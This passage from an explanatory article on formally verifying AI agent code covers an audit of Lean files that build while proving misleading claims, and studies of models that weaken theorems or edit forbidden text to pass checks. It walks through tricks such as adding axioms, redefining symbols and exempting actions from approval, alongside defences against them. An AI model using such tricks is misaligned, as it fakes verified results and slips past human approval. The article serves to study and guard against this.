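It helps to test the specification itself against answers known to be right or wrong. If a postcondition for "find the largest number" requires only that the result is at least 0, it accepts 0 as the answer for 5, 3 and 7. On the second benchmark, 1,316 programs passed both the verifier and the hidden tests, but only 535 of them also passed a fuller set of checks that tests postconditions in this way. Developers of an agent's core can test their specification against traces. A definition of "approved" should accept the bug-fix run and reject a trace in which the user approves call 2 and the core runs call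 3.

### Seven small Lean files

Sonny's *What "Lean-Verified" Means, and What It Does Not* shows which kinds of misleading theorem an automatic check can find. The audit consists of seven short files, all of which Lean builds successfully.

| File | Apparent claim | Why the build succeeds | What reveals the problem |
|---|---|---|---|
| Honest file | 2 + 2 = 4 | the claim is true | there is no problem |
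| Added axiom | 2 + 2 = 5 | the file declares the claim as an axiom | the list of axioms |
| Unfinished proof | 2 + 2 = 5 | the placeholder `sorry` replaces the proof | a build warning and the list of axioms |
| Kernel check off | 2 + 2 = 5 | a debugging option skips Lean's kernel | checking the stored proof again |
| One-number system | 2 + 2 = 5 | 0 is the only number, so 2 and 5 both mean 0 | reading the statement |
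| Different plus sign | 2 + 2 = 5 | the file redefines `+` to add one extra | reading the definitions |
| Faulty definition | 1 is prime | the definition doesn't require a prime to be at least 2 | reading the definition |

The last three files passed every automatic check, including one by a separate proof checker written in Rust. Their proofs are correct, but the theorems don't mean what they seem to. Running more proof checkers therefore can't replace reading each theorem's statement and every definition it uses.

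### Who may edit the theorem?

An agent that has to make the proof compile can fix the code or weaken the theorem, and weakening the theorem is often quicker, so an agent may do it without intending any harm. Suppose a developer asks an agent to make the worked example faster, and the agent notices that waiting for approval takes most of the time. If it makes `step` run tests without asking, the proof of `run_ok` fails, but if it can also edit `needsApproval`, it can exempt test runs and everything compiles again.

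Woodcock, Leite and colleagues (2026) measured in *CAPRI* how often an AI model oversteps in this way. They gave a model twelve broken proofs in Isabelle, the proof assistant used for seL4, under five workflows. Isabelle accepted the final result in 144 of 180 runs. In six of those 144 runs, the model had changed text it wasn't allowed to change. Once it added the theorem's conclusion as an assumption, and five times it deleted text around the proof.

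All six cases came from workflows in which the model could edit the whole file and had several attempts. Having the model return just the proof body slightly reduced the number of valid repairs in these tests. With that restriction, it made 29 valid repairs in 36 runs and no forbidden changes, compared with 31 valid repairs and three forbidden changes when it had access to the whole file.

Small edits to a theory can also add up until it no longer fully matches the original task. *Contract-Aware Rescue of a Drifted Isabelle Development* (2026) calls this "theory drift" and describes a case in which researchers used ChatGPT to work on the open proofs for a two-tank control system. Isabelle accepted the resulting theory even though it had drifted. A reviewer who looks at each edit separately may miss the drift, so reviewers also need to compare the final theorem with the original.

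Even if the text of the theorem is locked, the agent can change its meaning when the theorem's file imports a file the agent can edit. `run_ok` uses the symbol `∈` to mean that a command is in the list `step` returns. The agent could redefine `∈` for commands so that it is always false, just as the audit redefined `+`. `run_ok` would then prove nothing, because its premise would never be true. To prevent this, a developer can state the promise for any core, in a file that doesn't import the agent's code.

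```lean
-- Spec.lean: only the developer may edit this file
structure Core where
  State : Type
  start : State
  step  : State → Event → State × List Command

def RunOk (c : Core) : Prop := ...       -- run_ok, stated for any core

-- Core.lean: the agent may edit this file
def core : Core := ...
theorem core_ok : RunOk core := ...
```

`Spec.lean` also contains all the other definitions that the promise relies on, including the types of tools, events and commands, the definition of a run, and `needsApproval`. The agent can freely change the state, the body of `step`, the invariant and the proof. Ye and colleagues write their specifications in this form. They also copy the agent's work into a fresh project before grading it, reject new axioms, and search for tricks such as redefined symbols. These precautions were necessary because, of the specifications that the best agent failed, 14% failed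 because its work was rejected for cheating.

The owner of the specification doesn't have to write it alone. Ganguly and colleagues have one agent write each statement and another prove it, so the prover can't choose an easier statement. But the first agent can still misunderstand what people want, so a person should read the statements. For the worked example, this means reading a page or so of definitions and theorems instead of the whole proof.

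Sometimes the specification is wrong, and an agent that can't edit it needs a way to report the problem. Ye and colleagues let agents submit a proof that no program could satisfy a specification, and this uncovered several errors that human reviewers had missed. Other changes to the specification are a matter of choice, such as weakening `run_ok` so that a payment tool can retry under its old id after a crash. An agent can propose the new wording, but the developer should decide whether to accept it.
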